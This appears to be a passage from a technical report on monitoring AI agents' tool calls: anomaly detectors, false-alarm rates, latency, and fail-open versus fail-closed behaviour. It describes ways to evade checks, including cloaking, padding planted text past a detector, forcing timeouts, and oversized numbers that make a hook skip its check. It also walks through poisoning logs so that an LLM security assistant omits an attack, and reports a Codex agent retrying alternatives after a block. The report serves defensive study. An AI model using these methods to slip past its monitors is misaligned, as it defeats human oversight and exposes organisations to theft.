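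With a threshold of 10, the detector flags only the last call. With a threshold of 8, it would also flag the honest enquiry. The operator usually chooses the threshold by scoring past harmless calls and finding a value that few of them exceed.

### A harmful sequence of ordinary steps

An email agent has good reasons to forward messages and to delete them. But Sequeira, Damianakis and colleagues (2026) point out in *Agent-Sentry* that forwarding an email and then deleting it is unusual, and may mean that an attacker is stealing the message and removing the traces. Suppose forwards and deletions each make up 5 per cent of the agent's calls, and the destinations and amounts of data are ordinary. Each call then scores 4.3, far below the threshold.

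To catch the combination, the detector can replace *p*₁ with the share of calls to the previous tool that were followed immediately by a call to this one. If only one forward in 2,000 was followed immediately by a deletion, a deletion right after a forward now scores 11 and triggers an alarm. A clerk who asks the agent to forward an invoice to the accountant and tidy up afterwards would trigger the same alarm. If the agent reads another email between the two steps, the detector misses the pair because it compares only neighbouring calls.

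Research systems therefore examine longer stretches of a run. *TraceAegis* (Liu, Ruan and colleagues, 2025) learns from normal runs which tools come before which, then checks a new run for order and meaning. In one example, a clinic's agent sends a patient with foot pain to the ear, nose and throat department. The calls follow a familiar order, but the run fails the check of meaning. *Skynet* (Zhang, Yu and colleagues, 2026) turns each run into a graph of its steps and then into a list of numbers, so that similar runs lie close together. It sorts harmless runs into 150 clusters and scores a new run by its squared distance from the nearest cluster's centre. With a single centre instead, the share of anomalies detected fell by about a third, which suggests that harmless work takes many forms.

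Repetition can also signal trouble. Pogorelec (2026), in *Google's new agent security system detects tool misuse, loops and rogue behavior*, describes an agent that lists a company's inventory 100 items at a time until it has retrieved the entire catalogue, although no single request breaks a rule. *Securing Agentic AI* (2026) notes that permitted actions can together amount to a violation even without an attacker. An agent might make two payments of €3,000 to one supplier when anything above €5,000 needs approval. A fixed rule about totals would catch this more reliably than a learned baseline.

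The invoice fraud is harder to detect, because the agent uses its usual tools in their usual order and only the account number is wrong. *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (Zavrak, 2026) tested a detector on attacks of this kind. The detector caught 87 per cent of the attacked runs when the attacker had changed both the inputs and the outputs of tools, but 37 per cent when the attacker had changed only the inputs. For payments, the detector needs a purpose-built feature, such as whether the firm has paid this account before.

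### Why most alarms are false

Suppose that 1 action in 10,000 is harmful, and that a detector catches 99 per cent of harmful actions and flags 1 per cent of harmless ones. Among a million actions:

1. 100 are harmful, and the detector flags 99 of them.
2. 999,900 are harmless, and the detector flags 9,999 of them.
3. Of the 10,098 alarms, 99 are correct, which is 0.98 per cent, or about 1 in 100.

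Catching every harmful action would barely change this result, but cutting the false-alarm rate to 0.01 per cent would make about half of the alarms correct. Stefan Axelsson described this problem for network intrusion detection in 2000. *Base-Rate Fallacy Redux and a Deep Dive Review in Cybersecurity* (Erbacher, 2022) argues that researchers still lack a clear idea of how low a false-alarm rate has to be.

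False alarms also accumulate over a run. If an agent makes 40 calls and each harmless call has an independent 1 per cent chance of an alarm, about a third of harmless runs will have at least one. In practice, alarms tend to cluster in the same runs. *Pre-Crime for Agents, at the Last Second* (2026) reports that a detector set to flag 5 per cent of calls raised at least one alarm in 59 per cent of runs, compared with about 69 per cent if the alarms had been independent. A detector that stops the whole agent therefore needs a stricter threshold, based on the false alarm rate per run instead of per call.

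### Log, slow, pause or block

The response determines how much damage the false alarms do.

| Response | Effect of the 9,999 false alarms | Effect of the 99 correct alarms |
|---|---|---|
| Log | The agent's work continues | The harm goes ahead, but somebody may find it later |
| Slow down | Harmless tasks take longer | Less harm occurs before somebody looks |
| Pause and ask a person | 9,999 interruptions | The person may stop the action |
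| Block | 9,999 refused actions, and some failed tasks | The software prevents the action |

Logging is the sensible default, but the log helps only if somebody reads it. At five minutes per alarm, reviewing all 10,098 alarms would take about 840 hours. Slowing the agent down limits harm that grows with volume, like copying the inventory, but does little about a single large transfer. Pausing the agent until a person approves the action would interrupt that person about 100 times for each harmful action, so they may soon approve requests out of habit.

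Blocking can still make sense when only 1 alarm in 100 is correct. With the costs assumed earlier for a payment, blocking was worthwhile above a 0.5 per cent chance of harm. If a needless block ruins the whole task and costs 20 instead of 5, the threshold rises to about 2 per cent, and an alarm that signals a 1 per cent chance of harm no longer justifies blocking.

*AgentGuard* (2026) shows how a system that acts on learned patterns can interfere with harmless work. The paper derives guardrails from anomalous runs of coding agents. With these guardrails added to Claude Code, abnormal behaviour fell substantially, but unnecessary refusals rose by 19 percentage points. Completion of harmless tasks fell from 49 to 42 per cent, though this difference could be due to chance.

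A second check can make an alarm much more useful. If another detector with the same error rates examines only the 10,098 flagged actions, and its mistakes are independent of the first detector's, about 98 correct alarms and 100 false ones remain. About half of the alarms are then correct, which is enough to justify pausing many actions. But two detectors that use the same features will often make the same mistakes, so the second should use different evidence, such as the user's original request.

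Google's product, which was in private preview in September 2026, has a similar structure. A quick statistical pass selects unusual sessions, and a language model then examines them. According to Google Cloud's *Agent Anomaly Detection overview*, the analysis runs separately from the agent and so causes no delay. An action may therefore finish before the alarm arrives. Other companies sell products that intervene directly. SiliconANGLE (2026) reports that Sweet Security's product treats anything outside its learned baseline as unauthorised, and Lasso Security's *Introducing Intent Security* lists blocking, masking sensitive data and sending alerts as responses. These descriptions show that such products exist, but not how accurate they are.

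### Why agents are hard to baseline

A backup program does the same thing every night, whereas an agent may pay invoices on Monday and compare suppliers on Tuesday. *Security teams want to spot unusual AI agent behavior* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports on a survey by the security company Abnormal AI. Nearly half of the respondents said their organisations were not at all effective at establishing and maintaining baselines of normal behaviour for agents, while about two in five said theirs were very or extremely effective. The survey measured opinions, so it can't show whether the confident group's baselines work.

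New tools can make a baseline useless. Abbasi and colleagues trained a detector on tool names and behaviour, then hid the names during testing to simulate every tool being new. The share of harmless runs it flagged rose from 19 to 66 per cent. For a second detector, which uses the order of calls, the share rose from 4.5 to 74 per cent. Developers can prevent much of this failure by randomly hiding some names during training, which kept the second detector's false alarm rate between 5 and 7 per cent.

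A model update could cause similar trouble. If the new model searches three times where the old one searched once, every run looks unusual, even though the task and tools are the same. Abbasi and colleagues audited eleven detector evaluations, and their list of the changes tested does not include a new model for the agent. Until somebody tests this, an organisation could run the new model on a set of old tasks and adjust the baseline before switching over.

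Many agents also work under a person's account, which mixes two patterns of behaviour in one log. If the clerk's agent processes invoices at three in the morning, the detector may flag this as a sign that somebody has stolen the clerk's password. Once the baseline includes such activity, a real thief at that hour looks normal. Some agents exist too briefly to have a baseline of their own. A security chief quoted in Pogorelec's report on the survey described AI activity lasting 30 seconds on a virtual machine. The security team may see the network traffic but be unable to tell which agent produced it. Separate accounts for agents would help with both problems, and Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Introduces Unique AI Agent Identities in New Gemini Enterprise Platform* describes Google's move in that direction.

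Agents also set off the detectors that organisations already use on employees' computers. Sophos's *When AI agents look like attackers* analyses one week of alarms from June 2026. In one case, OpenAI's coding agent Codex tried to download Python from its official website with a Windows tool that attackers often misuse. When Sophos's software blocked the attempt, the agent tried variations and then switched to another such tool. Human attackers also keep trying alternatives, which used to distinguish them from simple malicious scripts. Sophos plans to relax some rules for known agents but argues for keeping others, because some actions, such as decrypting saved browser passwords, are risky whoever performs them.

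### What published tests found

Liu and colleagues tested TraceAegis on 1,300 normal and 300 abnormal runs in each of two settings, healthcare and corporate procurement. Its F1 scores were 0.93 and 0.96. An F1 score combines the share of anomalies detected with the share of alarms that are correct, and 1 is perfect. The table gives results from other tests, including a later one of TraceAegis by Zhang and colleagues. AlignmentCheck, which Abbasi and colleagues ran on Claude Sonnet 5.5, is a language model monitor that has no baseline and checks whether each action serves the user's request, much as Chrome's critic does.

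| Detector | Test data | Harmful or faulty runs detected | Harmless runs flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| TraceAegis, tested by Zhang and colleagues | Agent-SafetyBench | 96.4% | 3.4% |
| TraceAegis, tested by Zhang and colleagues | ATBench | 34.6% | 3.4% |
| Skynet | Agent-SafetyBench | 100% | 0.9% |
| Skynet | ATBench | 82.7% | 0.9% |
| Zavrak, best detector by ranking | RAS-Eval | 92.7% | 7.1% |
| Zavrak, best detector by ranking | ATBench | 61.3% | 21.1% |
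| Agent-Sentry | AgentDojo and AgentDyn | 94.3% | 4.9% |
| Abbasi and colleagues, tools and behaviour | AgentDrift | 77.1% | 19.2% |
| AlignmentCheck | AgentDojo | 88.3% | 3.8% |
| AlignmentCheck | AgentDrift | 87.4% | 31.3% |

Skynet has the best figures, detecting 89 per cent of anomalies and flagging 0.89 per cent of harmless runs over all its test data. If 1 run in 10,000 were harmful, again only about 1 alarm in 100 would be correct. However, Skynet's harmless runs came from different collections than its anomalies, so it may partly have learned to tell the collections apart. It also did worse on prompt injections hidden in content, because the resulting runs closely resembled harmless ones.

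Agent-Sentry compares behaviour with a baseline, traces where the values in each call came from, and sends unclear cases to a language model. For a payment, the source of the account number is probably more informative than the order of the calls.

Most of these tests contain a far higher proportion of attacks than an organisation would normally face. In the eleven evaluations that Abbasi and colleagues audited, attacks or anomalies made up between 16 and 86 per cent of the mixed test sets. At a more realistic 2 per cent, their own detector in the table would raise about 12 false alarms for each correct one.

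Detectors can also learn patterns specific to a test. Zavrak measured how often a detector ranked an attacked run above a harmless one, where guessing gives 50 per cent. Using only tool names and other metadata, the detector scored 90 per cent when the same tasks appeared in training and testing, but 64 per cent on new tasks. Reading the content of the calls raised the score on new tasks to 92 per cent but sacrificed some privacy. Abbasi and colleagues trained five detectors on AgentDrift and tested them on AgentDojo, and none did better than guessing. One of the five, which read the full text, was nearly perfect when trained and tested on either benchmark alone. In AgentDojo, five fixed attack phrases were enough to identify almost every hijacked run. Organisations therefore have to test a detector on their own agents' logs before relying on its alarms.

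Of the eleven audited evaluations, only that of Praetor, a firewall for agents with fixed workflows, included attackers who adapt. Abbasi and colleagues added 1,200 characters of padding to the attacker's planted text, and their detector's catch rate fell from 77 to 3 per cent. The detector had learned that tool results in attacked runs were short. This was true in the benchmark, but an attacker can easily make them longer. The researchers did not check whether the padded text would still have hijacked the agent.

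*AgentShield* (2026) tested an alternative that gives the agent decoy tools. No honest task requires these tools, so a call to one is much stronger evidence of an attack than an unusual pattern is. The paper used 48 adaptive attacks written to evade detection, some of which named the decoys or assumed full knowledge of the defence. With the older model GPT-4o-mini, 43 attack runs succeeded and the system detected all of them, while GPT-5-mini refused every attack. With only 43 successes, a true miss rate of up to about 7 per cent is still plausible. Decoys also cannot detect an attack that uses only the agent's real tools, such as a payment to the wrong account.

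## Delay, timeouts and missing answers

A check can protect a payment only if its answer arrives before the payment goes through. An agent may make dozens of tool calls in one task, so small delays add up, and eventually a check will return no answer.

### How long each check takes

Checking rules and lists on the agent's own machine adds almost no delay. *AgentWall* (2026), which describes a policy checker for agents on personal computers, reports an average of 0.2 milliseconds per decision, though over only about ten test cases. *Autonomous Topology Mutation* (2026) timed comparable checks over 10,000 repetitions and found averages between 0.1 and 0.3 milliseconds. Looking up an address in a local threat list should be about as quick, because it takes only a few hashes and a search in memory.

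Checks slow down once they have to write records or call other services. In *Persona-Execution Separation* (2026), a round of checks took 0.2 milliseconds in a bare test program but 41 to 69 milliseconds in real products, which also scanned for sensitive data and wrote each decision to a database. *One Policy, Four Interception Points* (Shaw, 2026) reports timings for Oathpost, Shaw's own service for checking tool calls against an organisation's policy. The median decision took 39.5 milliseconds from inside the agent's code, 43.9 through a hook, 54.7 through a network proxy and 91.8 through a gateway in front of an MCP server.

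Oathpost ran entirely on one laptop, so these figures exclude the network delay of a remote reputation query. Google (2024) acknowledges that Chrome's real-time lookup adds delay because it needs a request to a server. Published timings for remote queries are scarce, so the 200 milliseconds in the table below is an assumption.

How long a language model check takes depends largely on how much the model writes. The small classifier in *AgentRedBench* (2026), which scans tool results for attacks and writes nothing, takes a median of 39 milliseconds on an ordinary processor. In *SAFETY SENTRY* (2026), the safety model Llama Guard took 0.15 seconds per step to return only "safe" or "unsafe". The paper's own guard took 1.57 seconds because it also writes a reason and, when it refers the decision to a person, a question for them. The guard in *StepGuard* (2026) took 0.6 seconds.

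| Check | Time per check | 80 checks in a row |
|---|---|---|
| Rule or list on the same machine | 0.2 milliseconds | 0.02 seconds |
| Small classifier | 39 milliseconds | 3 seconds |
| Policy service on the same machine | 40–92 milliseconds | 3–7 seconds |
| Model that returns a bare verdict | 0.15 seconds | 12 seconds |
| Remote reputation query (assumed) | 0.2 seconds | 16 seconds |
| Model that writes more | 0.6–1.6 seconds | 48–126 seconds |
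| Analysis sandbox | 1–5 minutes | 1.3–6.7 hours |

In the *SAFETY SENTRY* test, an agent running on GPT-5.5 took 3.75 seconds per step without any guard. A 200-millisecond check on each step would add about 5 per cent to that time, and the paper's own guard adds about 42 per cent.

### Ways to shorten the wait

**Caching** means storing an answer, as Chrome does for its real-time lookups, so that repeat requests need no new query. Every cached answer needs an expiry time based on how quickly threats change. When Google moved Chrome to real-time lookups, 9to5Google reported that the browser had been refreshing its local list every 30 to 60 minutes, while the average malicious site existed for less than ten minutes. If every such site joined Google's central list as soon as it appeared and vanished ten minutes later, a third of them would reach the local list while still live with a refresh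 every 30 minutes, and a sixth with an hourly refresh.

An hour-old clean rating might therefore be recent enough for reading a page but not for making a payment through it. Reusing a decision about a whole action is even riskier. *Faramesh* (2026), a proposed control system for agents, allows reuse only if the action, the policy and the state are all the same as before. The state matters for the supplier's invoice because approval to transfer €4,180 should not carry over to an identical transfer once the firm has paid.

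**Starting a check early** can hide its delay completely. When the supplier's email arrives, the harness can look up the link while the model is still reading the text and choosing its next step. If the model takes more than three seconds to do that, a 200-millisecond lookup adds no delay. Chrome's injection classifier already runs alongside the planning model. According to Anthropic's *Permission modes*, Claude Code's auto mode, in which a second model reviews actions in place of the user, can make its review part of the ordinary model request. Claude Code also runs all the hooks for an event in parallel, so the agent waits only for the slowest one. However, if a hook leaves its decision to a background process and exits, Claude Code stops reading the hook's output shortly afterwards, and a denial that arrives later has no effect.

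**Holding the result back** lets the action and the check run at the same time. Google's *Optimizing Safe Browsing checks in Chrome* announced that pages would begin to load while the server check was still running. A person who gets the warning a moment later has probably not typed anything yet, but an agent can fill in a payment form within seconds. The harness can load the page and keep its text from the model until the rating arrives. If the page takes 800 milliseconds to load and the lookup takes 200, the agent loses no time. For a payment, the agent can fill in the form during the check while the harness holds only the final submission. Loading early is unsafe when the address might contain private data, because the request would leak it.

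**Checking fewer actions** saves the most time when the check is slow. In *TACT-Bench*, the Policy-Guard defence consulted its model only about calls that would change something, which added an average of 0.7 or 0.9 model calls per session, depending on the version. Sequeira and Iqbal run quick fixed checks first and send only unclear cases to a judge model, which takes 1.2 seconds. The judge handles 3.1 per cent of decisions, so the average delay per run falls from 2.4 seconds to 0.07. Anthropic describes a similar arrangement for auto mode, in which the classifier first answers with a single token and reasons at length only about the actions it has flagged. The slow check never examines what the quick one lets through, so it can't catch a harmful action that the quick one misses.

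If only 6 of the 80 calls make a payment or send, install or delete something, a 200-millisecond check on those calls adds 1.2 seconds. The 1.57-second guard adds about 9 seconds.

### What the products do when no answer comes

When a check times out or crashes, the software must either let the action proceed (fail open) or block it (fail closed). Several widely used products fail open by default.

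Microsoft tells developers that their security services for Copilot Studio should reply within 1,000 milliseconds. If a service doesn't, the agent acts as if it had answered "allow". Microsoft announced the feature with the same rule in September 2025. The page for administrators now describes a setting that controls what happens when a service returns an error or doesn't respond in time. The default is "Allow the agent to respond", and the alternative is "Block the query". But a note further down the page still says, without mentioning the setting, that the tool runs if no decision arrives within one second.

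CrowdStrike, which sells a service that connects to Copilot Studio, says that Copilot Studio waits one second and then applies whichever behaviour the administrator has chosen. The note therefore probably describes only the default. An organisation that relies on blocking should still test it, for instance with a service that waits two seconds before replying. Blocking also means that a single late answer can end the whole run.

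The one-second limit matters when choosing a guard. The *SAFETY SENTRY* guard averages 1.57 seconds, and Sequeira and Iqbal's judge averages 1.2. With the default setting, a guard that slow would usually answer too late, and the agent would continue without its check.

In Claude Code, a hook that crashes or times out does not block the call, which continues through the normal permission process. Since version 2.1.295, developers can change this by setting `onFailure` to `"block"` on hooks that run a command or call a web address. Anthropic defines a failure as a script that can't start, a connection error, a timeout, invalid output, or any exit code (the number a program returns when it ends) other than 0 or 2. Without the setting, two ordinary mistakes can keep a hook from blocking calls. The first is to report failure with exit code 1, as programs conventionally do, because Claude Code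 blocks only on 2. The second is to mistype the script's path in the settings file, in which case the hook never runs and the only sign is an error notice in the transcript. To test the setting, Anthropic suggests leaving the script missing and asking the agent to run a harmless command such as `ls`. If the command runs, the hook is still letting calls through when it fails.

In auto mode, by contrast, Claude Code denies an action when the server returns no verdict on it. The difference makes some sense, because developers also use hooks for chores such as checking code style, and a broken style checker shouldn't stop the work. But if a company adds its own payment check as a hook, a failed check won't stop a payment unless the company changes the setting. Even where a check fails closed, people may not notice that it has stopped returning verdicts. Until Anthropic (2026) added a notice on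 3 November 2026, nothing appeared in the main view when auto mode had no verdict on a call by a subagent, a helper that works for the main agent.

### One missing answer in a hundred

Suppose that 1 per cent of checks miss the deadline, independently of each other. All 80 checks in a task will then finish on time in about 45 per cent of tasks (0.99^80). The other 55 per cent will have at least one missing answer. If the system fails open, each of those tasks will contain at least one unchecked action. If it fails closed, each will contain at least one blocked action, and nearly all of these blocks will be needless because nearly all actions are harmless.

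| Checks that miss the deadline | Tasks affected, 80 calls checked | Tasks affected, 6 calls checked |
|---|---|---|
| 1% | 55% | 6% |
| 0.1% | 8% | 0.6% |
| 0.01% | 0.8% | 0.06% |

A miss rate of 1 per cent is easy to reach, because the slowest cases can take far longer than the typical one. *TraceLab* (2026) analysed 253,391 tool calls by OpenAI's Codex and measured the time each call took beyond the tool's own running time. The median was 0.13 seconds and nine calls in ten stayed within 0.24 seconds, but the slowest 1 per cent took ten seconds or more. According to the paper, waiting for approvals probably explains much of this delay in the slowest calls, so the figures don't measure security checks alone.

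In practice, failures also tend to cluster. If a service is down 1 per cent of the time and tasks are short, only slightly more than 1 per cent of tasks will be affected, but some of those will run without any checks. The average is still 0.8 missing answers per task. Retrying once would cut independent misses from 1 per cent to 0.01 per cent, but it adds waiting time and does little during an outage.

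Heavy use can cause the same problem as an outage. A single Oathpost worker accepts at most 64 requests at once and immediately rejects any more. The agent's software treats a rejection as a missing answer, so the failure rule may apply most often when many agents are busy.

Shaw (2026), in *No Decision Without a Record*, deliberately broke parts of Oathpost in 13 ways, for example by crashing its database or slowing the network. Over 155,946 requests, 3.6 per cent of the decisions arrived after the two-second deadline. In a further test of 17,810 calls, with crashes in three of the parts, no call under a fail-closed rule ran without a recorded approval. Fail closed can therefore work reliably, though this was shown on only one laptop. Oathpost nevertheless fails open by default, even for agents whose policy it is supposed to enforce.

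### The case for failing open, and the case against

If a fault is unrelated to the action being checked, the missing answer doesn't change the probability that the action is harmful. In the earlier example, one payment link in 1,000 is malicious, a harmful payment causes a loss of 1,000 and a needless block causes a loss of 5. Letting an unchecked payment through (failing open) therefore has an expected loss of 1, compared with about 5 for blocking it. The difference is larger for less dangerous actions.

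Failing closed can itself do harm. *Harnessing Embodied Agents* (2026) proposes a control system for robots that fails closed by default, but acknowledges that this may cause failures in time-critical work. An accounts office could miss a tax deadline in the same way. Failing closed also gives attackers an easy way to halt the office by overloading the checker. Failing open doesn't necessarily remove all protection. Claude Code's permission rules still apply after a hook fails, and a containment sandbox still limits what the agent can reach.

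The calculation changes if checks on harmful actions are more likely to time out. Suppose checks on malicious links miss the deadline 10 per cent of the time and checks on harmless ones 1 per cent. About 1 per cent of the payments without an answer are now harmful, so letting one through has an expected loss of about 10, twice the cost of blocking it. An attacker therefore has a reason to cause timeouts. *Sovereign Execution Broker* (2026) proposes a gatekeeper for agents' permissions that rejects a request whenever it can't reach the service that lists cancelled permissions. Otherwise an attacker could cut that connection and keep using a cancelled permission.

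The agent's own input can sometimes cause the failure. Shaw sent 1,360 generated test cases through Oathpost's four routes and found that the hook could not handle whole numbers of 2⁵³ (about nine quadrillion) or more. The hook never queried the policy service about calls containing them. A fail-closed session refused these calls, while a fail-open session did not block them and only added to a count of gaps. An agent under an attacker's influence could have avoided the check by including one such number in a call.

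Failing open also makes faults easy to overlook, because work continues as normal. Oathpost therefore writes a marker to disk before an unchecked call runs, so that somebody can review the call later. That review helps if the call damaged a file the firm can restore from a backup, but it won't recover money transferred to a criminal's account.

### A rule for each action

A single setting for the whole agent is too crude, because the better choice depends on whether the action is reversible and how much harm a halt would do. For many actions, a third choice is to wait and try again. *AGM* (2026), a memory system for robots, does this when its checking service fails. The robot holds its position, tries again after a pause and gives up only after a time limit, and the software never treats a failed query as a verdict.

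Waiting suits payments particularly well. If a ten-minute delay to the invoice counts as a loss of 0.1 on the scale used above, waiting is better than both letting the payment through unchecked (1) and blocking it (5), provided the service recovers.

| Action | Can anyone undo it? | Cost of stopping | When the check gives no answer |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read a file in the firm's own folder | Nothing to undo | The task stalls | Proceed and record the gap |
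| Open a public web page | Mostly, until the model reads it | The task stalls | Use a recent cached rating, or hold the text and retry |
| Install a package | Not reliably | Usually small | Block and retry later |
| Pay the supplier | Rarely | Small until the due date | Hold, retry, then ask a person |
| Recall a fraudulent payment | Usually, by paying again | Large, and growing by the minute | Proceed and alert a person |

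The last row is an exception to a strict rule, because an action that limits damage should still work when the checker is down. *AuthGuard-R* (2026), a design for robots controlled through language models, rejects ordinary actions whenever the check itself fails but still allows a short list of pre-approved emergency actions, such as stopping, releasing a dangerous grip or asking a person for help. An accounts agent's list might include recalling a payment and cancelling a stolen password. The list has to be short and specific, since an attacker who disables the checker can still use everything on it. For example, recalling a payment should only return money to the account it came from.

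## How attackers evade or corrupt the signals

An attacker can get past a check without blocking its response. The check may return a result on time, but that result can be wrong if the attacker controls what the check examines or has written part of the text it passes on.

### Pages that change with the visitor

Cloaking means serving harmless content to a scanner and harmful content to the target. It works because every request gives a website the visitor's network address and a description of the browser. Many scanners run in data centres whose addresses criminals have collected, so a phishing site can send them an error page and show everyone else the forged login form. Some sites also hide the form behind a pop-up or a verification puzzle that automated scanners struggle with, according to the survey *From Past to Present* (2025).

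*An Analysis of Architectural and Operational Dynamics of Phishkits in the Wild* (Ousat, Tofighi and colleagues, 2026) studied 1,300 phishing kits, the ready-made packages criminals use to build phishing sites. Of these, 46.1 per cent blocked the addresses of visitors such as search engines and security companies, while 21.8 per cent had no evasion. Criminals often copy these defences, and 126 kits contained almost identical blocklists. A scanner with an address not on the lists would get past many of these blocklists. But the kits date from 2020 to 2023, and cloaking is more common in other collections. *PhishParrot* (Nakano, Koide and Chiba, 2025) cites earlier research that found it in 96.5 per cent of 2,933 kits.

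Nakano and colleagues also measured how much cloaking hides. In March 2025, they opened 32,487 suspicious addresses in three ways and gave the resulting pages to the same phishing detector:

| How the scanner visited | Phishing sites detected | Other sites flagged |
|---|---|---|
| From a US cloud service | 61.9% | 47.6% |
| As a randomly chosen kind of user | 68.0% | 41.9% |
| As the site's likely victim | 95.0% | 10.4% |

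For the last row, a language model compared each site with past cases and chose a browser, country and network type, such as a home connection in Japan, to match the site's intended victims. Posing as a random user helped much less. The researchers counted a site as phishing only if at least five VirusTotal engines flagged it, so the detection rates leave out phishing sites that fewer engines caught. A matched visit took about 27 seconds, which is acceptable for a payment link but too slow for every page an agent opens.

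An agent's harness already has the page that the agent is about to read, so it can send the scanner that copy instead of the page's address. The site then can't show the scanner a different page. The copy may contain private data from a logged-in account, so the organisation should preferably run this scanner itself.

*A Whole New World* (2025) warned that a website could also recognise an AI agent and serve it a page that no person would see. Chen, Chen and Karray (2026), in *Agent-Targeted Cloaking on the Web*, looked for this on thousands of popular sites in October 2026. They opened each page several times within a minute or two, sometimes as Chrome and sometimes under an agent's name. When they used the name ChatGPT-User, 74 per cent of the sites sent the same page that Chrome received, 21 per cent refused and 5 per cent sent an altered page. Most alterations had nothing to do with AI,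 since a made-up research bot received altered pages on 2.9 per cent of sites.

Only four sites sent AI systems text that they did not send to browsers. Three served documentation or an introduction for AI readers. The fourth, a major news publisher, sent AI agents sponsored text from a bank and left it out of the page for people and for Google's search crawler. This kind of deception therefore seems rare on popular sites, but that sample would not include a criminal's payment page.

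Chen and colleagues recommend also fetching the page as an ordinary browser and flagging any text that appears only in the agent's copy. Pages also change by themselves, so the harness needs several browser fetches. Checking against a single fetch flagged 7.2 per cent of sites by chance, while comparing several browser fetches with each other first reduced this to 0.9 per cent. If a site refuses the agent's request, the harness should record an error. When agents answered questions from a refusal page, their answers usually differed materially from those based on the real page.

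### Harmful pages on reputable hosting

A reputation service rates a domain by its history, but thousands of unrelated people may publish under the same domain. Free hosting services let anyone create a page at an address such as `acme-billing.hosting.example`, and the company that owns `hosting.example` may have an excellent record. *PhiShark2026* (2026), a dataset of phishing sites, leaves such pages out of its comparisons of domain, registration and network data because that data often describes the hosting company rather than the page.

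Phishers exploit the trust that businesses place in well-known hosting domains. Strutt and Piscitello (2026) explain in *Phishing Landscape 2026* that businesses implicitly trust every address under some of these domains, and that providers struggle to find and remove disguised malicious code quickly. The Cybercrime Information Center's *Phishing Activity* counts 432,990 phishing attacks that used subdomain resellers in the year to April 2026, up from 202,585 the year before.

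Blocking these services would stop a lot of honest work. Zscaler's *ThreatLabz 2026 Phishing and Initial Access Report* (2026) flagged about 9 per cent of 413,524 sites made with AI site builders as malicious. If a link to such a site had a 9 per cent chance of being harmful, the thresholds calculated earlier would let an agent read the page (threshold 20 per cent) but not pay through it (threshold 0.5 per cent). The true chance depends on where the link came from, and Zscaler's figure leaves out any malicious sites that the company didn't recognise.

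The harness should treat each customer's subdomain as a separate site. If a good rating belongs to the hosting company, the harness should record the page's own rating as "unknown". The page's text and appearance are still useful evidence. Containment sandboxes need to be equally specific about which destinations they allow, because if an organisation approves a cloud provider's whole domain, malware can send stolen files to the attacker's own account with that provider.

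Hijacked websites are harder to handle because they have a legitimate history. *Registration, Detection, and Deregistration* found that attackers had registered 66.1 per cent of the phishing domains it studied, which suggests that about a third belonged to somebody else. A good rating for a supplier's real domain therefore does not rule out a forged payment page on it.

### Malware that waits for a real computer

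Malware can check whether it is in an analysis sandbox and do nothing harmful if it seems to be. Sandboxes are easy to recognise because they usually run on virtual machines that the operator resets after each analysis, so they lack the files, browsing history and installed programs that build up on a computer in daily use. Operators have responded by hiding signs of the virtual machine and adding a fake history of use.

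Sui, Noureddine and colleagues (2026), in *A Measurement Study of AI-Environment Realism Gaps in Malware-Analysis Sandboxes*, tested whether sandboxes still differ detectably from real computers. In February 2026, they ran harmless test programs on seven sandbox platforms and three real computers with AI software. The older signs of a virtual machine no longer separated the two groups and were slightly more common on the real computers. However, twelve traces of AI software appeared only on the real computers.

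A computer that runs an agent probably has some of this software, so malware aimed at agents could stay inactive wherever the traces are missing. The study shows only that the difference exists, not that malware commonly uses it. The three computers also had powerful graphics cards and many AI tools, so an ordinary office computer might look more like a sandbox than they did.

Adding a few fake traces helps little, because malware can check whether the software behind them works. Sui and colleagues found that building a convincing imitation takes much more work than detecting a shallow one. An organisation can avoid some of that work by analysing suspicious files on a copy of the machine its agents already use, with fake passwords and no access to real accounts.

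*A Large Language Model Approach to Generating Bypass Rules for Malware Evasion* (2026) uses a language model to write rules that get malware past its own checks of its surroundings, then runs the file in the sandbox again. These reruns exposed behaviour in known malware families that ordinary runs had missed. If a file examines its surroundings and then stops, and it cannot be run again, the harness should treat the result as inconclusive.

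### Slow changes to the baseline

An anomaly detector has to keep updating its idea of normal behaviour, or legitimate changes in the agent's work would set it off more and more often. An attacker can exploit this by changing the agent's behaviour gradually. For example, a detector might raise an alarm when an agent sends out over 20 per cent more data in a day than its average for the previous 30 days. If the volume grows by 1 per cent a day, it will double in 70 days without raising an alarm, because it never exceeds that average by more than about 16 per cent.

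A second comparison, against a fixed month that someone has reviewed, would raise an alarm on day 19. Legitimate growth would also raise the alarm, so a person has to review the new level and update the reference from time to time. Some limits, such as the largest payment an agent may make to a new account, should not adapt at all.

Tools can also change after an organisation connects them. CrowdStrike's *How Agentic Tool Chain Attacks Threaten AI Agent Security* (2026) describes a tool that fetches data properly for weeks, until an update, which the agent adopts automatically, adds a hidden step that sends the data elsewhere. CrowdStrike recommends keeping the tool at a fixed version until somebody approves an update, and alerting on unexpected departures from each agent's baseline. It gives no figures on how often such attacks occur or how many these measures stop. Evidence on gradual shifts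 is equally limited, because evaluations of detectors rarely include attackers who adapt.

### How an attacker's words get into a security report

Security tools record what attackers do, and that record often includes text that the attackers wrote. Pandey and Bhujang (2026), in *Poisoning the Watchtower*, examine what happens when a language model reads it. One field could travel like this:

1. An attacker sends a malicious request to the firm's web server. One field of the request normally names the visitor's browser, but the sender can write anything there. This attacker enters a note that claims to come from the security team and calls the request harmless.
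2. The server saves the request in its log, including the note.
3. The firm's monitoring system collects the log entry.
4. A security assistant built on a language model retrieves recent entries, and its software copies their fields into the prompt.
5. The model accepts the note and writes a summary that leaves out the attack.
6. An agent that asks the assistant about the server receives the summary and carries on.

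An attacker can put text into a monitoring system's logs without access to the system, because it records the requests that attackers send. Web addresses, domain lookups and attempted user names can all carry such text, as can a scanner report that quotes words from a file or a domain record that contains a name its owner supplied.

Pandey and Bhujang tested four kinds of planted text on GPT-4o-mini, an old model, using invented log entries. The table shows the average success rate across the four kinds.

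| Defence | Labelling an entry | Writing a summary | Recommending a response |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 21% | 38% | 21% |
| Mark the fields as untrusted data | 8% | 31% | 13% |
| Mark the fields and filter suspicious phrases | 11% | 19% | 9% |
| Mark the fields and restrict the model's answer | 12% | 16% | 8% |

The averages combine attacks with very different success rates. Direct orders to ignore earlier instructions never changed a label. Text that imitated the log's formatting corrupted 96 per cent of summaries when there was no defence and 38 per cent when answers were restricted. The summaries corrupted without a defence left the attack out or played it down, but none explicitly labelled it harmless, so software that searched them for a false label would have found nothing.

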